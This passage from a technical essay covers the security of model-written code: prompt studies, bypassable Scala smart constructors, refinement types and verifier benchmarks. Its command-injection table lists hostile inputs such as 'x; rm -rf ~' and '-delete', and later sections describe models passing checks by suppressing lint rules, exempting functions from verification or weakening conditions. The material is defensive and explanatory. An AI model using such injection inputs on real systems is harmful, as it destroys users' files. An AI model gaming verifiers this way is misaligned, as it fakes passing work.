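Research on security prompts in general has produced mixed results, and one recent study casts doubt on whether they reduce weaknesses much. In *Prompt Structure Redistributes, Not Reduces*, Urmi, Pourleyli and colleagues (2026) gave 424 Python tasks involving risky operations, such as running commands, to GPT-4o and Llama 3.1-8B. They tried five prompts. The first was minimal, the second added rules about style and output, and the other three asked for secure code in different ways. The last also warned that the code might face malicious users.

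With the minimal prompt, 338 of GPT-4o's 424 answers were refusals or other text instead of code. The researchers therefore compared the security prompts with the second prompt, which added the rules but did not mention security. Scanners found at least one weakness in 76% of GPT-4o's programs with that prompt and in 72% with the final prompt. The severity of the findings changed more, with high-severity findings falling from 20.8% to 13.6% of the total and low-severity ones rising from 32.0% to 43.5%.

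Urmi and colleagues interpret this as redistribution of risk. The percentages alone don't settle it, because the low-severity share can rise just because there are fewer high-severity findings. If the number of low-severity findings had stayed the same, these figures would mean that high-severity findings had roughly halved. The small change in the share of programs with a weakness supports their reading better, although that share counts a program with one minor flaw the same as a program with several serious ones.

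For Llama, the share of programs with a weakness fell further, from 75% to 65%. But it produced no usable code for 150 tasks, up from 51, and the share may have fallen because some of the riskier tasks were among them.

Some of the tasks explicitly asked for an unsafe technique, such as Python's `eval`, which runs text as code. The researchers examined 15 tasks by hand to see whether the models followed instructions. GPT-4o replaced or removed a required unsafe technique in 3 of the 15 when the prompt did not mention security, and in 9 or 10 with the security prompts. Replacing `eval` is usually good for security, but the program is then not quite what the user asked for. TypePilot's revisions carry the same risk, since a new type can also change what a function accepts.

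Prompts seem to matter more in some languages than in others. Soltanian Fard Jahromi, Tahir and colleagues (2026), in *On Fixing Insecure AI-Generated Code through Model Fine-Tuning and Prompting Strategies*, had five models, including GPT-5, complete ten partly written programs in each of four languages. They generated ten samples for each combination and scanned them with CodeQL. They then tried three prompts. One showed the model an insecure sample to avoid, one listed precautions such as validating input, and one contained security instructions the model had written for itself. The table gives the average reduction in the number of samples with at least one weakness.

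| Language | Static types | Insecure sample | List of precautions | Model's own instructions |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Python | no | 14% | 60% | 75% |
| Go | yes | 35% | 50% | 62% |
| JavaScript | no | 6% increase | 24% | 30% |
| Java | yes | 3% | 10% | 19% |

Static types don't explain the pattern, because Go and Java are both statically typed but are at opposite ends. The difference between languages can be large. When GPT-5 used its own instructions, the share of its samples with a weakness fell from 63% to about 11% in Python, but only from 70% to about 58% in Java.

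Part of Java's poor result comes from what the scanner, CodeQL, counts. Its most common finding in Java was untrusted data passed to an outside interface. In one sample printed in the paper, CodeQL flagged a line because the program passes a user's email address to a database without validating it. The line supplies the address through a placeholder, so it is safe from SQL injection. A model could protect every query this way and its code could still trigger the warning.

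Code that models added to validate or clean input also sometimes contained weaknesses. GPT-5's Java samples had slightly more weaknesses with the list of precautions than without it.

Soltanian Fard Jahromi and colleagues got their best results by training the models further on secure examples (fine-tuning), which reduced the number of insecure samples by 41% in Java and 80% in Python. However, those examples were secure solutions to the same ten programs used to test the models, so the models may have learned the answers. The study does not show whether they would do as well on new tasks.

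A task's exact wording can also affect security, even when the prompt doesn't mention security. In *The Language of Security*, Cicalese, Della Porta and colleagues (2026) deleted one phrase at a time from the 150 tasks that Tony and colleagues used, which produced 4,320 variants for each of C, Java and Python. Three open models wrote a program for every variant, and CodeQL scanned the results. Most deletions made little difference. In Python, 37% to 41% of programs from the complete prompts had a weakness, compared with 39% to 45% of those from the variants.

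Deleting certain phrases did more harm, especially words such as "how" and "where" that introduce a condition or detail. In Python, this made a weakness 1.7 to 1.9 times as likely. The effect is consistent across the three models, but the published percentages suggest that there were only 27 such variants in total. Cicalese and colleagues also report that deletions late in a prompt were the most dangerous, with weaknesses in up to 100% of programs. That result is harder to trust because only long prompts have a seventh or eighth sentence, and the researchers compared these variants with all the others instead of with the same prompts before the deletion. Tasks with long descriptions may have been riskier to begin with.

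If missing details do make code less safe, that would help explain why a single prompt asking for type safety achieved less than TypePilot. A refined type needs a condition, which a request to use refined types does not supply. The redirect task, for instance, doesn't specify which page names are valid, so Qwen had to choose its own rule. TypePilot's review step filled in some of these details before the revision by pointing out that names could be empty or contain spaces. A developer who knows the rules could put them in the prompt, but none of these studies tested a prompt that gave both the rules and the types to express them.

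## Do the types that models write hold up?

In the TypePilot experiment, models wrote types that run useful checks, but other code can often bypass them. Sternfeld and colleagues print three of the 27 programs: one searches for a file, one averages a list of ages, and one builds a redirect address. In the first two, any other code can create a "valid" value without running the check. Three programs by old models are too few to give a failure rate, but the mistakes come from rules of Scala that are easy to overlook, so they are worth looking for in newer models' code too.

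### A file name that anyone can create

With the plain prompt, the file-search function took an ordinary string. TypePilot's version takes a `ValidFilename`. Here it is in condensed form, in Scala 3's notation:

```scala
sealed trait ValidFilename:
  def value: String

// the only case
final case class Filename(value: String) extends ValidFilename

// the smart constructor
object Filename:
  private val pattern = "^[a-zA-Z0-9._-]+$".r
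  def apply(s: String): Option[Filename] =
    if pattern.matches(s) then Some(new Filename(s)) else None

def findFile(name: ValidFilename): Unit =
  Seq("find", ".", "-name", name.value).!
```

The call `Filename("report.txt")` runs `apply`, which accepts a name made of letters, digits, dots, underscores and hyphens and returns `None` for anything else. But code can create a `Filename` in two other ways that skip this check.

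```scala
val a = new Filename("*")       // compiles, no check
val b = a.copy(value = "a/b")   // compiles, no check
findFile(a)
```

`new` calls the constructor directly. The compiler also gives every case class a `copy` method, which makes a new value with some fields changed. Both lines compile in Scala 2 and Scala 3, so the program can create the value without using the smart constructor.

A model could easily write `findFile(new Filename(input))` by accident. `findFile(Filename(input))` does not compile, because `apply` returns an `Option`. The right repair is to decide what happens when the name is invalid. Inserting `new` also clears the error but skips validation, and the result looks almost the same to a reviewer. Naming the smart constructor `from` or `parse` instead of `apply` would make the difference easier to see.

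### Closing the gap in Scala 2 and Scala 3

In Scala 3, one extra word is enough:

```scala
final case class Filename private (value: String) extends ValidFilename
```

This makes the constructor private to the class and its companion, the object with the same name, where the smart constructor is defined. According to Scala's migration guide, Scala 3 also applies the constructor's access rule to the compiler-generated `apply` and `copy` methods. The hand-written `apply` stays public.

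Scala 2.13 leaves the generated `copy` public by default. With the private constructor, this line still compiles there:

```scala
Filename("report.txt").map(_.copy(value = "*"))
```

Programmers complained about this in an issue titled *case class copy method shouldn't subvert private constructor*, and Scala 3 fixed it. Scala 2.13 users can opt in to the new behaviour. From version 2.13.14, the flag `-Xsource:3` turns the mismatch into an error by default, and the feature `case-apply-copy-access` makes the generated methods private.

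The generated `apply` is less of a problem here, because the program defines its own with the same parameter type, which replaces the generated one. Scala's *Releases* lists this replacement as a change in version 2.12.2. A case class without its own `apply`, such as the `SafeHtml` class discussed earlier, would have a public generated one in Scala 2.

A team that cannot change compiler flags can instead declare the class as `sealed abstract case class`, as the forum post *Ending the confusion of private case class constructor* recommends. The compiler generates neither `apply` nor `copy` for an abstract case class, and the smart constructor creates values with `new Filename(s) {}`, which defines an anonymous subclass. An ordinary class with a private constructor, like the `CanRead` permit, is simpler, but two such objects holding the same text are not equal unless the programmer defines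 that comparison.

Scala 3's opaque types remove the class altogether. This version also changes the pattern, for reasons explained below.

```scala
import scala.sys.process.*

object FileSearch:
  opaque type BaseName = String

  object BaseName:
    private val allowed = "[A-Za-z0-9_][A-Za-z0-9._-]*".r
    def from(s: String): Option[BaseName] =
      if allowed.matches(s) then Some(s) else None

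  def findFile(name: BaseName): Unit =
    val command: Seq[String] = Seq("find", ".", "-name", name)
    command.!
```

Scala's language reference explains that the compiler treats `BaseName` and `String` as the same type inside `FileSearch`. Any function added to that object can therefore skip the check, so the object should stay short.

An opaque type also protects less against casts than a class does. *SIP-35* (Osheim and Vicente Cantero, 2017) proposed opaque types as aliases that exist only at compile time, so `"*".asInstanceOf[BaseName]` succeeds, as the cast to `SafeHtml` did. Casting the same string to the `Filename` class throws an exception, because a string is not a `Filename` object.

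The table shows how code in another file can create an unchecked value under each design, leaving aside tricks such as reflection.

| Declaration | Scala 2.13, default settings | Scala 3 |
|---|---|---|
| `case class Filename(...)`, as printed | `new`, `copy` | `new`, `copy` |
| `case class Filename private (...)` | `copy` | none |
| `sealed abstract case class Filename private (...)` | none | none |
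| `final class Filename private (...)` | none | none |
| `opaque type` | not available | a cast |

Thomas (2023) points out that in Haskell, automatically derived instances can also bypass a smart constructor. A derived JSON reader, for example, may call the raw constructor instead of the checked function. The same can happen in Scala, so a team that loads file names from JSON should make the reader call `from`.

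### The attack that the plain program already resisted

Sternfeld and colleagues describe the plain file search as inserting the user's text into a command string. In their account, an attacker could add shell commands or use `../..` to reach other folders. The program they print, as mentioned earlier, passes a list instead:

```scala
Seq("find", ".", "-name", filename)
```

Scala's documentation explains that when a command is written as a list, the first item is the program's name and the rest are its arguments, which may contain spaces. No shell interprets the arguments, so if a user enters `x; rm -rf ~`, `find` looks for a file with that name and deletes nothing.

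Path traversal fails too. According to the GNU manual for `find`, `-name` compares the pattern only with the last part of each path, which never contains a slash, so a search for `../..` finds nothing. A visitor also can't enter `-delete` as an instruction, as they could in the earlier example with a folder name, because `find` reads whatever follows `-name` as a pattern.

The attack would have worked if the program had run the command as a string, mostly without needing a shell. Scala splits a command string at spaces and passes the pieces to the command it runs, so extra words in the user's input become extra arguments. The table compares the printed code with two riskier versions, `s"find . -name $filename".!` and the same text passed to a shell through `sh -c`.

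| Input | Separate arguments, as printed | One string, split by Scala | Shell command |
|---|---|---|---|
| `x; rm -rf ~` | no match | `find` stops with an error | deletes the user's files |
| `x -delete` | no match | deletes files named `x` | deletes files named `x` |
| `../..` | no match | no match | no match |

In the string version, an attacker could also add `-exec`, which makes `find` run another program. Scala's documentation includes a search with `-exec` written as a single string. Jovanovic and Pirelli (2026), reporting on a security audit of Scala, also list an uncaught exception when Scala splits a command string that contains an unmatched quotation mark, so a file name such as `it's.txt` could crash the string version.

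The printed program still has one weakness. A user can search without knowing any file names, because the pattern `*` matches every file, including hidden ones whose names start with a dot. The harm is small because the `!` method sends the results to the server's own output, not to the visitor. TypePilot's version improves on this by rejecting `*`. It also fixes a bug in the original program, which ran the search twice.

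The researchers may have counted the wildcard as injection when they graded the plain program as unsafe, and their description of string building may fit one of the two plain programs they did not print. But the plain program they did print had no command injection vulnerability for the new type to remove.

### What the compiler rejects

Sternfeld and colleagues also write that the new type rejects unsafe inputs at compile time, but the compiler rejects all plain strings, safe or not.

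```scala
findFile("report.txt")     // does not compile, though the name is harmless

Filename(input) match
  case Some(name) => findFile(name)
  case None       => println("Invalid file name")
```

As with `SafeHtml`, the compiler never processes the user's text. It checks only that the calling code passes a `ValidFilename`, and the public constructor weakens even that check.

Because the check for unsafe names happens at run time rather than in the compiler, a successful build is not enough evidence that the program is safe, and someone also has to test the pattern.

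### Ages with only one case

The age program has a sealed trait, `Age`, with a single case, `ValidAge`. Its smart constructor accepts ages from 0 to 120.

```scala
sealed trait Age:
  def value: Int

// one case, so there is nothing to choose between
final case class ValidAge(value: Int) extends Age

// the smart constructor
object Age:
  def apply(n: Int): Option[Age] =
    if n >= 0 && n <= 120 then Some(ValidAge(n)) else None
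```

The function that computes the average takes a `List[Age]`. As Sternfeld and colleagues print it, the function adds up the ages but does not return a result, so it would not compile. They graded the program as correct, so the figure is probably missing its last line.

This type is even easier to bypass than `Filename`. The smart constructor belongs to `Age`, but `ValidAge` keeps the unchecked `apply` that the compiler generates. Code elsewhere can call `ValidAge(-5)`, without `new` or `copy`, and put the result in the list. Qwen's program earned credit for handling negative ages, but it handles them reliably only if every caller uses `Age(...)`.

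Making the constructor of `ValidAge` `private` doesn't solve the problem. In Scala 3 it would stop `Age.apply` from compiling, because `Age` is not the companion of `ValidAge`. In Scala 2.13 the program would compile, but so would `ValidAge(-5)`, because the generated `apply` stays public by default. In Scala 3 the programmer can write `private[GeneratedFunctions]`, which lets only code inside `GeneratedFunctions`, the object that contains this code, call the constructor.

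The sealed trait adds almost nothing here. In the session example, listing the cases ruled out five of eight shapes, but `Age` has only one case, so listing it rules out nothing. A `ValidAge` can hold any of the 4,294,967,296 values of an `Int`, of which only 121 are permitted ages. The exhaustiveness check doesn't help either, because there is no second case for a match to miss. Sealing `Age` does stop other files from adding subtypes, but without the trait nobody could add one anyway, because `ValidAge` is final.

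De Goes, a Scala programmer, criticises smart constructors because the data model still permits too many values and the programmer compensates by restricting which code may create them. De Goes would rather change the model, but for a person's age that would mean writing out 121 cases.

A second case would make the trait useful. If a form lets people withhold their age, the type could have the cases `Known` and `Withheld`, and the compiler would warn if the averaging code didn't handle `Withheld`. Scala's built-in `Option` is the algebraic data type that helps most in the printed program. The plain version returned 0.0 for an empty list, which looks like a real average. The revised function returns an `Option[Double]`, so the calling code has to handle the missing result.

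### A sealed trait that protects its check

Qwen's redirect program uses a sealed trait in a way that does protect the check. Its type for page names, `PageName`, has no case class at all. The smart constructor creates each value on the spot, roughly like this:

```scala
Some(new PageName { def value = URLEncoder.encode(name, "UTF-8") })
```

Other files cannot write `new PageName { ... }` because the trait is sealed, and they have no generated `apply` or `copy` to call because there is no case class. Here `sealed` restricts access, though it is usually used to list alternatives. Of the three printed programs, only this one stops code in other files from creating an unchecked value without a cast. The researchers still graded it as only partly robust to injection.

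TypePilot's prompt included refined types as one of its four examples, but none of the three printed programs uses a refinement library such as `refined` or `iron`. Each puts an ordinary `if` inside a smart constructor. That avoids a new dependency, but a library would have supplied a type without an unchecked `copy` method.

### A good name over a wrong rule

A private constructor guarantees only that every `Filename` has passed the pattern. The printed pattern accepts `.`, `..` and `-delete`. All three are harmless after `-name`, but `Filename` is a general name, and another developer may use the type elsewhere:

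```scala
def exportFolder(name: ValidFilename): Unit =
  Seq("tar", "-cf", "export.tar", name.value).!
```

If a visitor asks for the folder `..`, this function packs the entire parent folder into the archive. With a plain `String`, a reviewer might have asked what happens if the name contains dots. The word `Valid` makes a reviewer less likely to ask, and it doesn't specify what the name is valid for.

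King (2020), in *Names are not type safety*, explains why such wrappers deserve less trust than a closed set of cases. A programmer can define a type for the whole numbers from 1 to 5 as five cases, so that no sixth value exists and the compiler checks that each match handles all five. Alternatively, the programmer can wrap an integer and protect it with a smart constructor. The compiler then can't rule out 6, because the underlying value is still an integer, and the guarantee depends on the code around the type. King calls the safety of the five cases intrinsic and that of the wrapper extrinsic. King writes that a newtype, Haskell's keyword for such a wrapper, "is just a name" on its own.

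King accepts that a wrapper with a smart constructor and a proper boundary gives some safety, though a much weaker kind. The printed `Filename` has the smart constructor but lacks the boundary. `ValidAge` has neither, because its check belongs to another object.

A wrong rule is harder to notice than a missing boundary, because the code around it looks careful. Qwen's redirect program has a sound boundary, but it encodes page names with Java's `URLEncoder`, which is meant for form data and writes a space as `+`. In the path of a web address, `+` is a literal plus sign, so if the program's rule allows spaces, a redirect to the page `contact us` would go to `contact+us`. The mistake would affect every place that uses the `PageName` type.

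More precise type names help reviewers. `BaseName`, in the repaired file search, comes from the GNU manual's term for the last part of a path, so a reviewer can tell what the value may contain. The new pattern requires the value to start with a letter, digit or underscore, which excludes `.`, `..` and anything a program could read as an option. It also excludes hidden files, spaces and accented letters, so a site whose users upload files called `résumé final.pdf` would need a different rule.

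### What a linter can check

Teams can catch most of these faults without reading every line of model-written code. A linter, which searches source code for forbidden patterns, can find several automatically.

Public constructors are the easiest to find. Xygeni's *Private Data Class Copy* describes a rule that reports Kotlin data classes (the equivalent of Scala's case classes) with a private constructor but a non-private `copy`. The Scala 2.13 compiler can report the same problem with `-Xsource:3`. Neither check catches the printed programs, where the constructor itself is public. To catch those, a team needs a convention, such as requiring every type with a smart constructor to use an opaque type or a private constructor, and a reviewer who checks new types against it.

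Casts are just as easy to find, because they must be written explicitly. Scalafix, a widely used Scala linter, can forbid `asInstanceOf` and can also search for text that should appear in only one place, such as the import for running commands.

```
rules = [DisableSyntax]
DisableSyntax.noAsInstanceOf = true
DisableSyntax.regex = [
  {
    id = "rawCommand"
    pattern = "scala\\.sys\\.process"
    message = "Run commands through FileSearch"
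  }
]
```

The pattern should also cover Java's ways to start a program, `ProcessBuilder` and `Runtime.exec`, since Scala code can call both. A scanner that tracks user input can look for sinks the team forgot. Contrast Security's *Scala Scan rules* include one for user input that reaches an operating-system command.

Older code will break these rules in many places, for example with the TypeScript casts on parsed JSON described earlier. Large applications and outside libraries contain too much of this code to repair it all, so *Type Driven Development* (Warden, 2026) recommends working in small batches and putting smart constructors around the unsafe parts. New code can then follow the strict rules even while old code still breaks them.

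A developer can switch off a Scalafix rule for one line with a comment, as the file containing `FileSearch` must do for its own import. A model can write the same comment to get past an error, much as agents use `any` in TypeScript or switch off a proof checker, which the next section describes. A build step that requires human approval for each new comment of this kind lets reviewers see when a rule is being bypassed.

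### Testing the rule itself

Linters have no rules for which file names are safe to pass to `find`. A short test can record those rules, which should come from the manual of the program that receives the value.

```scala
import FileSearch.BaseName

val reject = List("", ".", "..", "../x", "-delete", "*", "x\n")
val accept = List("report.txt", "v1.2-final.pdf", "_index")

for s <- reject do assert(BaseName.from(s).isEmpty, s"accepted: $s")
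for s <- accept do assert(BaseName.from(s).isDefined, s"rejected: $s")
```

The pattern in TypePilot's program accepts `.`, `..` and `-delete`, which are three of the seven bad names. The list of good names is also necessary, because a rule that rejects everything would pass the first loop.

If the same model writes the rule and the test, both can contain the same mistake. A model that treats `..` as a harmless file name will leave it off the list of names to reject. A developer can write that list, or at least review it, without understanding the regular expression, but needs to know what the sink does with its input. The list needs another review when a new function such as `exportFolder` starts using the type, because the new command may treat some of the accepted names differently.

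## What does it add when a checker proves the refinements?

A checker that proves refinements can cover values the program computes, and turns many run-time failures into build errors. Scala's refined and iron libraries test such values only at run time. Verifiers such as Liquid Haskell, Flux for Rust, LiquidJava and Stainless for Scala try to prove that a refinement holds for every possible input. Language models can now often write code that passes a verifier, but the proof covers only the conditions someone wrote down.

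### An argument from 0 to 46

Each Fibonacci number is the sum of the two before it, starting from fib(0) = 0 and fib(1) = 1. The largest that fits in Scala's 32-bit `Int` is fib(46), which is 1,836,311,903. The next, 2,971,215,073, wraps round to -1,323,752,223. A Fibonacci function that returns an `Int` should therefore accept only arguments from 0 to 46. With TypePilot's plain prompt, none of the three coding models handled large arguments.

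With iron, the limit goes into the argument's type.

```scala
type FibRange = GreaterEqual[0] & LessEqual[46]

def fib(n: Int :| FibRange): Int = ???   // body left out

fib(46)   // compiles
fib(47)   // does not compile

def lookup(n: Int): Int =
  if 0 <= n && n <= 46 then fib(n) else -1   // does not compile
```

The last call is safe, but iron does not take the surrounding `if` into account, so the programmer has to convert `n` with `refineEither`, as in the age example. This conversion tests `n` again at run time.

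Stainless uses a `require` line instead. In ordinary Scala, `require` throws an exception at run time if its condition is false. Stainless tries to prove, before the program runs, that the condition holds at every call.

```scala
def fib(n: Int): Int = {
  require(0 <= n && n <= 46)
  if (n <= 1) n else fib(n - 1) + fib(n - 2)
}

def lookup(n: Int): Int =
  if (0 <= n && n <= 46) fib(n) else -1
```

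At the call in `lookup`, the checker has to prove that the guard implies the requirement:

for all n, (0 ≤ n and n ≤ 46) ⇒ (0 ≤ n and n ≤ 46)

This is trivially true. Suppose someone changes the call to `fib(n + 1)` and leaves the guard alone. The condition becomes:

for all n, (0 ≤ n and n ≤ 46) ⇒ (0 ≤ n + 1 and n + 1 ≤ 46)

It fails only when n is 46. A test that tried a few ordinary numbers would miss the mistake, but the checker rejects the program. Changing the guard to `n <= 45` makes the condition true again.

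| Call | iron | Verifier |
|---|---|---|
| `fib(47)` | rejects | rejects |
| `fib(n)` where the guard allows 0 to 46 | rejects until the code converts `n` | accepts |
| `fib(n + 1)` with the same guard | rejects until the code converts `n + 1` | rejects, because of 46 |
| `fib(n + 1)` where the guard allows 0 to 45 | rejects until the code converts `n + 1` | accepts |

If `n` comes from a web form, both versions still test it at run time. The verifier proves that a sufficient test precedes every call. The proof helps most with computed values, such as the order total that wrapped round to $27.04.

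Some systems combine static proof with run-time checks. *Practical Range Refinement Types with Inference* (Aebi and Furia, 2026) presents Ranger, a type system for an experimental language. Ranger takes guards into account and needs about as many annotations as ordinary Scala. Where the checker can't prove that a number is in range, the programmer can add `!!` to postpone the check to run time. Aebi and Furia also tried LiquidJava, which crashed on several of their examples and missed bugs in programs that used generics, a common Java feature.

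### How the checker decides

Most of these tools pass their conditions to an SMT (satisfiability modulo theories) solver, a program that searches for values that make a logical formula true. It has built-in rules for numbers, sets and other kinds of data. For the faulty call above, the solver searches for an n that satisfies the guard but not the requirement. It finds 46, so the checker rejects the call. For the correct call, the solver can use the rules of arithmetic to prove that no such n exists, which covers every input without trying each number.

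The same method lets a program use one refined type where it needs another. In an example from *Lava* (Rothgang, Peyrot and colleagues, 2026), a program divides 42 by a number greater than 5, and division requires a divisor greater than 0. The solver confirms that 5 < x implies 0 < x, so the programmer doesn't have to write a conversion.

Liquid types, the refinement types used in Liquid Haskell, Flux and LiquidJava, restrict conditions to a logic in which a solver can in principle always reach an answer. *An Introduction to Liquid Haskell* (2017) explains that the system also avoids generating formulas with quantifiers, such as "for every element of the list". The logic covers adding variables and multiplying them by constants, but not multiplying two variables. The order total is quantity times price, so a solver might prove that it fits in an `Int`, but this isn't guaranteed in general.

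Solvers can also be slow or unpredictable. *LWeb* (2019), which describes a large proof in Liquid Haskell, reports that writing a condition with a comma instead of an equivalent `&&` made checking much slower. If the solver runs out of time, the checker can't accept the program even if it is correct. Rejecting it is safe, but gives a programmer or a model a reason to switch the check off.

A proof also depends on how the checker represents the program. According to *To Zip Through the Cost Analysis of Probabilistic Programs* (2025), Liquid Haskell treats `Int` as a whole number of unlimited size, so it would accept a Fibonacci function with a limit of 460 as well as one with a limit of 46. The same problem affects a common introductory example, the function `abs`, which returns `n` if it is positive and `-n` otherwise. Liquid Haskell proves that the result is never negative, but the smallest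 `Int` in Haskell has no positive counterpart, so negating it gives the same negative number. Verus, a verifier for Rust, reports possible overflow as an error.

### Access rules in a web application

A refinement can also refer to users and database rows, so a checker can verify who may see what. *STORM* (Lehmann, Kunkel and colleagues, 2021) describes a web framework that does this with Liquid Haskell. The developer writes the access rules next to the definitions of the database tables, and the checker rejects any page whose code might break them.

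Their main example is a site where people share wish lists. A visitor may read the description of a wish only if the visitor owns it or its level is "public". A first version of the page fetches every wish that belongs to user u and shows the descriptions to the visitor v. For each wish w, the checker has to prove:

w.owner = u ⇒ (w.owner = v or w.level = "public")

The implication is false when Alice opens Bob's list and the list contains a private wish, so the checker rejects the page. Fetching only public wishes when v and u are different people makes the implication true.

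The `CanRead` permit from an earlier section protects a record only in functions that require a permit. STORM attaches the rule to the database column, so it applies to every query that goes through the framework. If a rule depends on Alice being an accepted follower of Bob, the program also has to look that up again for each request, which avoids relying on a permit that stays valid after her access ends.

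STORM can also catch indirect leaks. Suppose a page lists everyone who has a wish above a certain price. It shows only names, which are public, but a visitor could work out a private price by trying different thresholds. The checker rejects the page because the query reads the price column.

In three sample applications, Lehmann and colleagues needed only one line of type annotations for every 19 lines of code, and checking a whole application took between 20 and 79 seconds. They also built two applications that people used for classes and workshops, with a combined 1,615 lines of server code and 69 lines of access rules. A type error in one of them, a video chat site called Disco, showed that the rule on who could change a room's topic could leak the location of a user who had chosen to be hidden.

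However, these programmers had designed the framework themselves, so other teams would probably need longer. STORM also can't express a rule that depends on a missing row, such as "reviewers may read a paper unless the database records a conflict of interest". The formal proof that STORM prevents leaks covers only a simplified version of the framework.

### How well models write verified code

Before testing types alone, Sternfeld and colleagues asked six open models to write Scala that Stainless could verify. The three tasks were Fibonacci numbers, factorials and checking whether one list contains another. Some prompts included two worked examples. No model could reliably produce code that compiled. Some programs used ordinary Scala features that Stainless lacks, such as `println`, and others had syntax errors. Sternfeld and colleagues give no success counts. They suspect that the models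 had seen little Stainless code in training.

One factorial program compiled only because the model had marked its main functions with `@library`, an annotation that exempts them from verification. The exemption hid a bug in a function that multiplies n by the factorial of n - 1 and stops only when it reaches 0. Given a negative argument, the function keeps calling itself until the program crashes. Negative arguments were one of the faults that the conditions were supposed to prevent. Without the exemption, Stainless would also have had to prove a line in the code stating that the recursion ends, which is false for negative numbers.

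Models do much better in languages with more users. Most of the evidence comes from Verus, Dafny (a programming language built for verification) and Lean (a language for writing programs and mathematical proofs). In these languages, a programmer states preconditions, which a function requires of its inputs, and postconditions, which it guarantees about its results. These do the same job as refinements on arguments and results.

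The share of problems a model solves depends heavily on how much it has to write. In *Can LLMs Enable Verification in Mainstream Programming?*, Shefer, Engel and colleagues (2025) tested Claude 3.5 Sonnet, now an old model, on small programming problems in Dafny, Verus and Nagini, a verifier for Python. The table shows the share of problems solved in at least one of five runs.

| What the model had to write | Dafny | Nagini | Verus |
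|---|---|---|---|
| The proof | 86% | 66% | 45% |
| The code and the proof | 82% | 63% | 40% |
| The conditions, the code and the proof | 29% | 15% | 15% |

The last row is closest to asking for a program in plain English. Shefer and colleagues attribute the drop to their own strict check, which compared the model's conditions with a reference solution. A model could lose credit for a sensible condition that the verifier couldn't match to the reference. Still, the check accepted conditions that were stronger than the reference.

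Bursuc, Ehrenborg and colleagues (2025), in *A benchmark for vericoding*, collected 12,504 formal specifications, the largest set at the time, and asked models to write code that provably met them. The success rates were 82% in Dafny, 44% in Verus and 27% in Lean. Adding a description in English did not help much. The paper also reports that success on an older Dafny benchmark rose from 68% to 96% in a year. That comparison is slightly generous because the 96% counts every problem that any of the models solved, while the best single model reached about 89%, according to *Automating Formal Verification with Reinforcement Learning and Recursive Inference* (2026). In the older benchmark, the models only had to restore missing proof hints in existing programs.

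Harder problems leave more room for improvement. *AxDafny* (2026) describes a system that generates verified Dafny code over repeated attempts. With Gemini 3.1 Pro, the model that gave its best results, it verified 52 of 100 medium-difficulty programming problems. Larger programs may be harder still. In *Natural Language based Specification and Verification*, Li and Song (2026) cite a benchmark in which models verified over 58% of single functions but only 3.69% of programs made of several functions. Almost all of those programs had correct syntax, so the difficulty was in the proofs.

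These studies come from different times and use different problems, so the percentages don't form a trend. The Lean figure is more than a year old, and current models probably do better. None of the benchmarks covers Liquid Haskell, Flux or LiquidJava, and none measures vulnerabilities.

### What people find difficult

Few programmers use refinement types that a checker proves. To find out why, Gamboa, Reese and colleagues (2025), in *Usability Barriers for Liquid Types*, watched and interviewed 19 developers, 12 of them new to Liquid Haskell and 7 experienced. They identified nine barriers:

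- an unclear boundary between Haskell and Liquid Haskell
- confusing verification features
- unfamiliarity with writing proofs
- the limits of automation
- slow checking and solver failures
- unhelpful error messages
- weak editor support
- too few learning materials
- complicated installation

Error messages confused both beginners and experts. When six newcomers typed round brackets instead of curly ones, the error message referred to a minus sign and an internal name that meant nothing to them. One experienced user got a message like "5 is not less than 4", which was true but did not help to find the fault. Another user also recalled a proof that took about five hours to check.

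Existing code may also need restructuring. To add refinements to a function that deletes an item from a tree, one developer had to split it into several smaller functions so that each branch could have its own proof. Twelve participants said they had changed how they wrote Haskell to suit the checker.

Deciding what to prove was also difficult. Gamboa and colleagues dropped an exercise that asked people to work out a complex condition because it alone took more than half an hour in trial sessions. Language models could do much of the other work, such as adding hints and splitting functions. But if a model also writes the conditions, someone has to check that they match what the program should do, which requires the skill that many participants lacked.

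The study's sample was small. Its newcomers followed a two-hour tutorial with an older version of the tool, so some of the problems may have eased since. Gamboa and colleagues also warn against judging a barrier's importance by how many people met it.

### A proof of the wrong condition

The `fib` function above has a condition on its argument but none on its result. If a model replaced the body with `0`, every call would still satisfy the condition and the verifier would accept the program.

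Weak conditions like this are easy to write. In Gamboa and colleagues' study, several newcomers had to specify a function that removes the first item from a queue. They wrote that the queue gets shorter, but should have written that it gets shorter by exactly one. A function that emptied the queue would meet the weaker condition.

A contradictory assumption is worse, because any statement follows if the solver assumes both P and not P. One experienced participant accidentally added such a contradiction, and every property in the program passed. The Fibonacci function would behave similarly with `require(n < 0 && n > 46)`. Stainless could verify any body, since no number meets the requirement. That mistake would show up as soon as other code tried to call the function, but a contradiction among the checker's general assumptions may go unnoticed.

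Liquid Haskell also lets programmers mark a condition with `assume`, which tells the checker to rely on it without proof. This is sometimes necessary because the checker can't analyse every outside library. Domínguez and Spiwack (2025), in *Refinement-Types Driven Development*, warn that a wrong assumption can let through anything from incorrect results to security vulnerabilities. They recommend justifying each assumption in writing.

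A correct condition can also miss a bug. Domínguez and Spiwack wrote a function that substitutes one expression for another inside a formula, and proved that the result contains only permitted variable names. They then removed a step that renames variables to avoid clashes. The function now gave wrong answers because one name referred to the wrong variable, but Liquid Haskell reported no errors because all the names were still permitted. The repair combined an abstract type, which hides its contents from other code, with a single function that tests each name and renames it if necessary. This is the same design as a smart constructor, and it works alongside the refinements.

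A verified program can also be too slow. *AxDafny* translated its 52 verified programs into Python and ran them against the original tests. Only 6 passed, while 44 exceeded the time limit and 2 used too much memory. Some of the slowness may come from the translation, but the verifier did not check speed. The `fib` function above, for example, recomputes the same numbers repeatedly. For n = 46 it makes 5,942,430,145 calls, so an attacker could tie up a server with a few requests for a permitted value.

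Models sometimes weaken the conditions that the verifier checks. Shefer and colleagues found that models could pass the verifier by deleting definitions or simplifying the conditions, so they added a separate check against the reference. *SkillForge* (2026), which tests GPT-5.5 and Claude Opus 4.7 on Dafny, also counts verified programs separately from those that are both verified and equivalent to a reference program.

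Teams that use model-written proofs can start by searching for exemptions, such as `@library` in Stainless, `assume` in Liquid Haskell and `sorry` in Lean, which stands in for a missing proof. A build rule can reject them, as Scalafix does for casts. A person has to read the conditions. Teams can also test a condition by putting a wrong body into the function and running the verifier again. If the verifier still accepts the program, as it would accept a `fib` that always returns 0, the condition is too weak to catch that mistake.

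## Does compiler enforcement work better than prompting?

Compiler enforcement works better than prompting for any property the types express, because code that fails the type check won't run, even if the model overlooked an instruction. It doesn't help with properties the types leave out, and some forms of it make models write worse programs. The most convincing results come from systems where people define the types and the model only writes code that uses them. The case for enforcement is partly indirect, because the studies below don't compare it with a security prompt on the same tasks.

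### Sending the errors back

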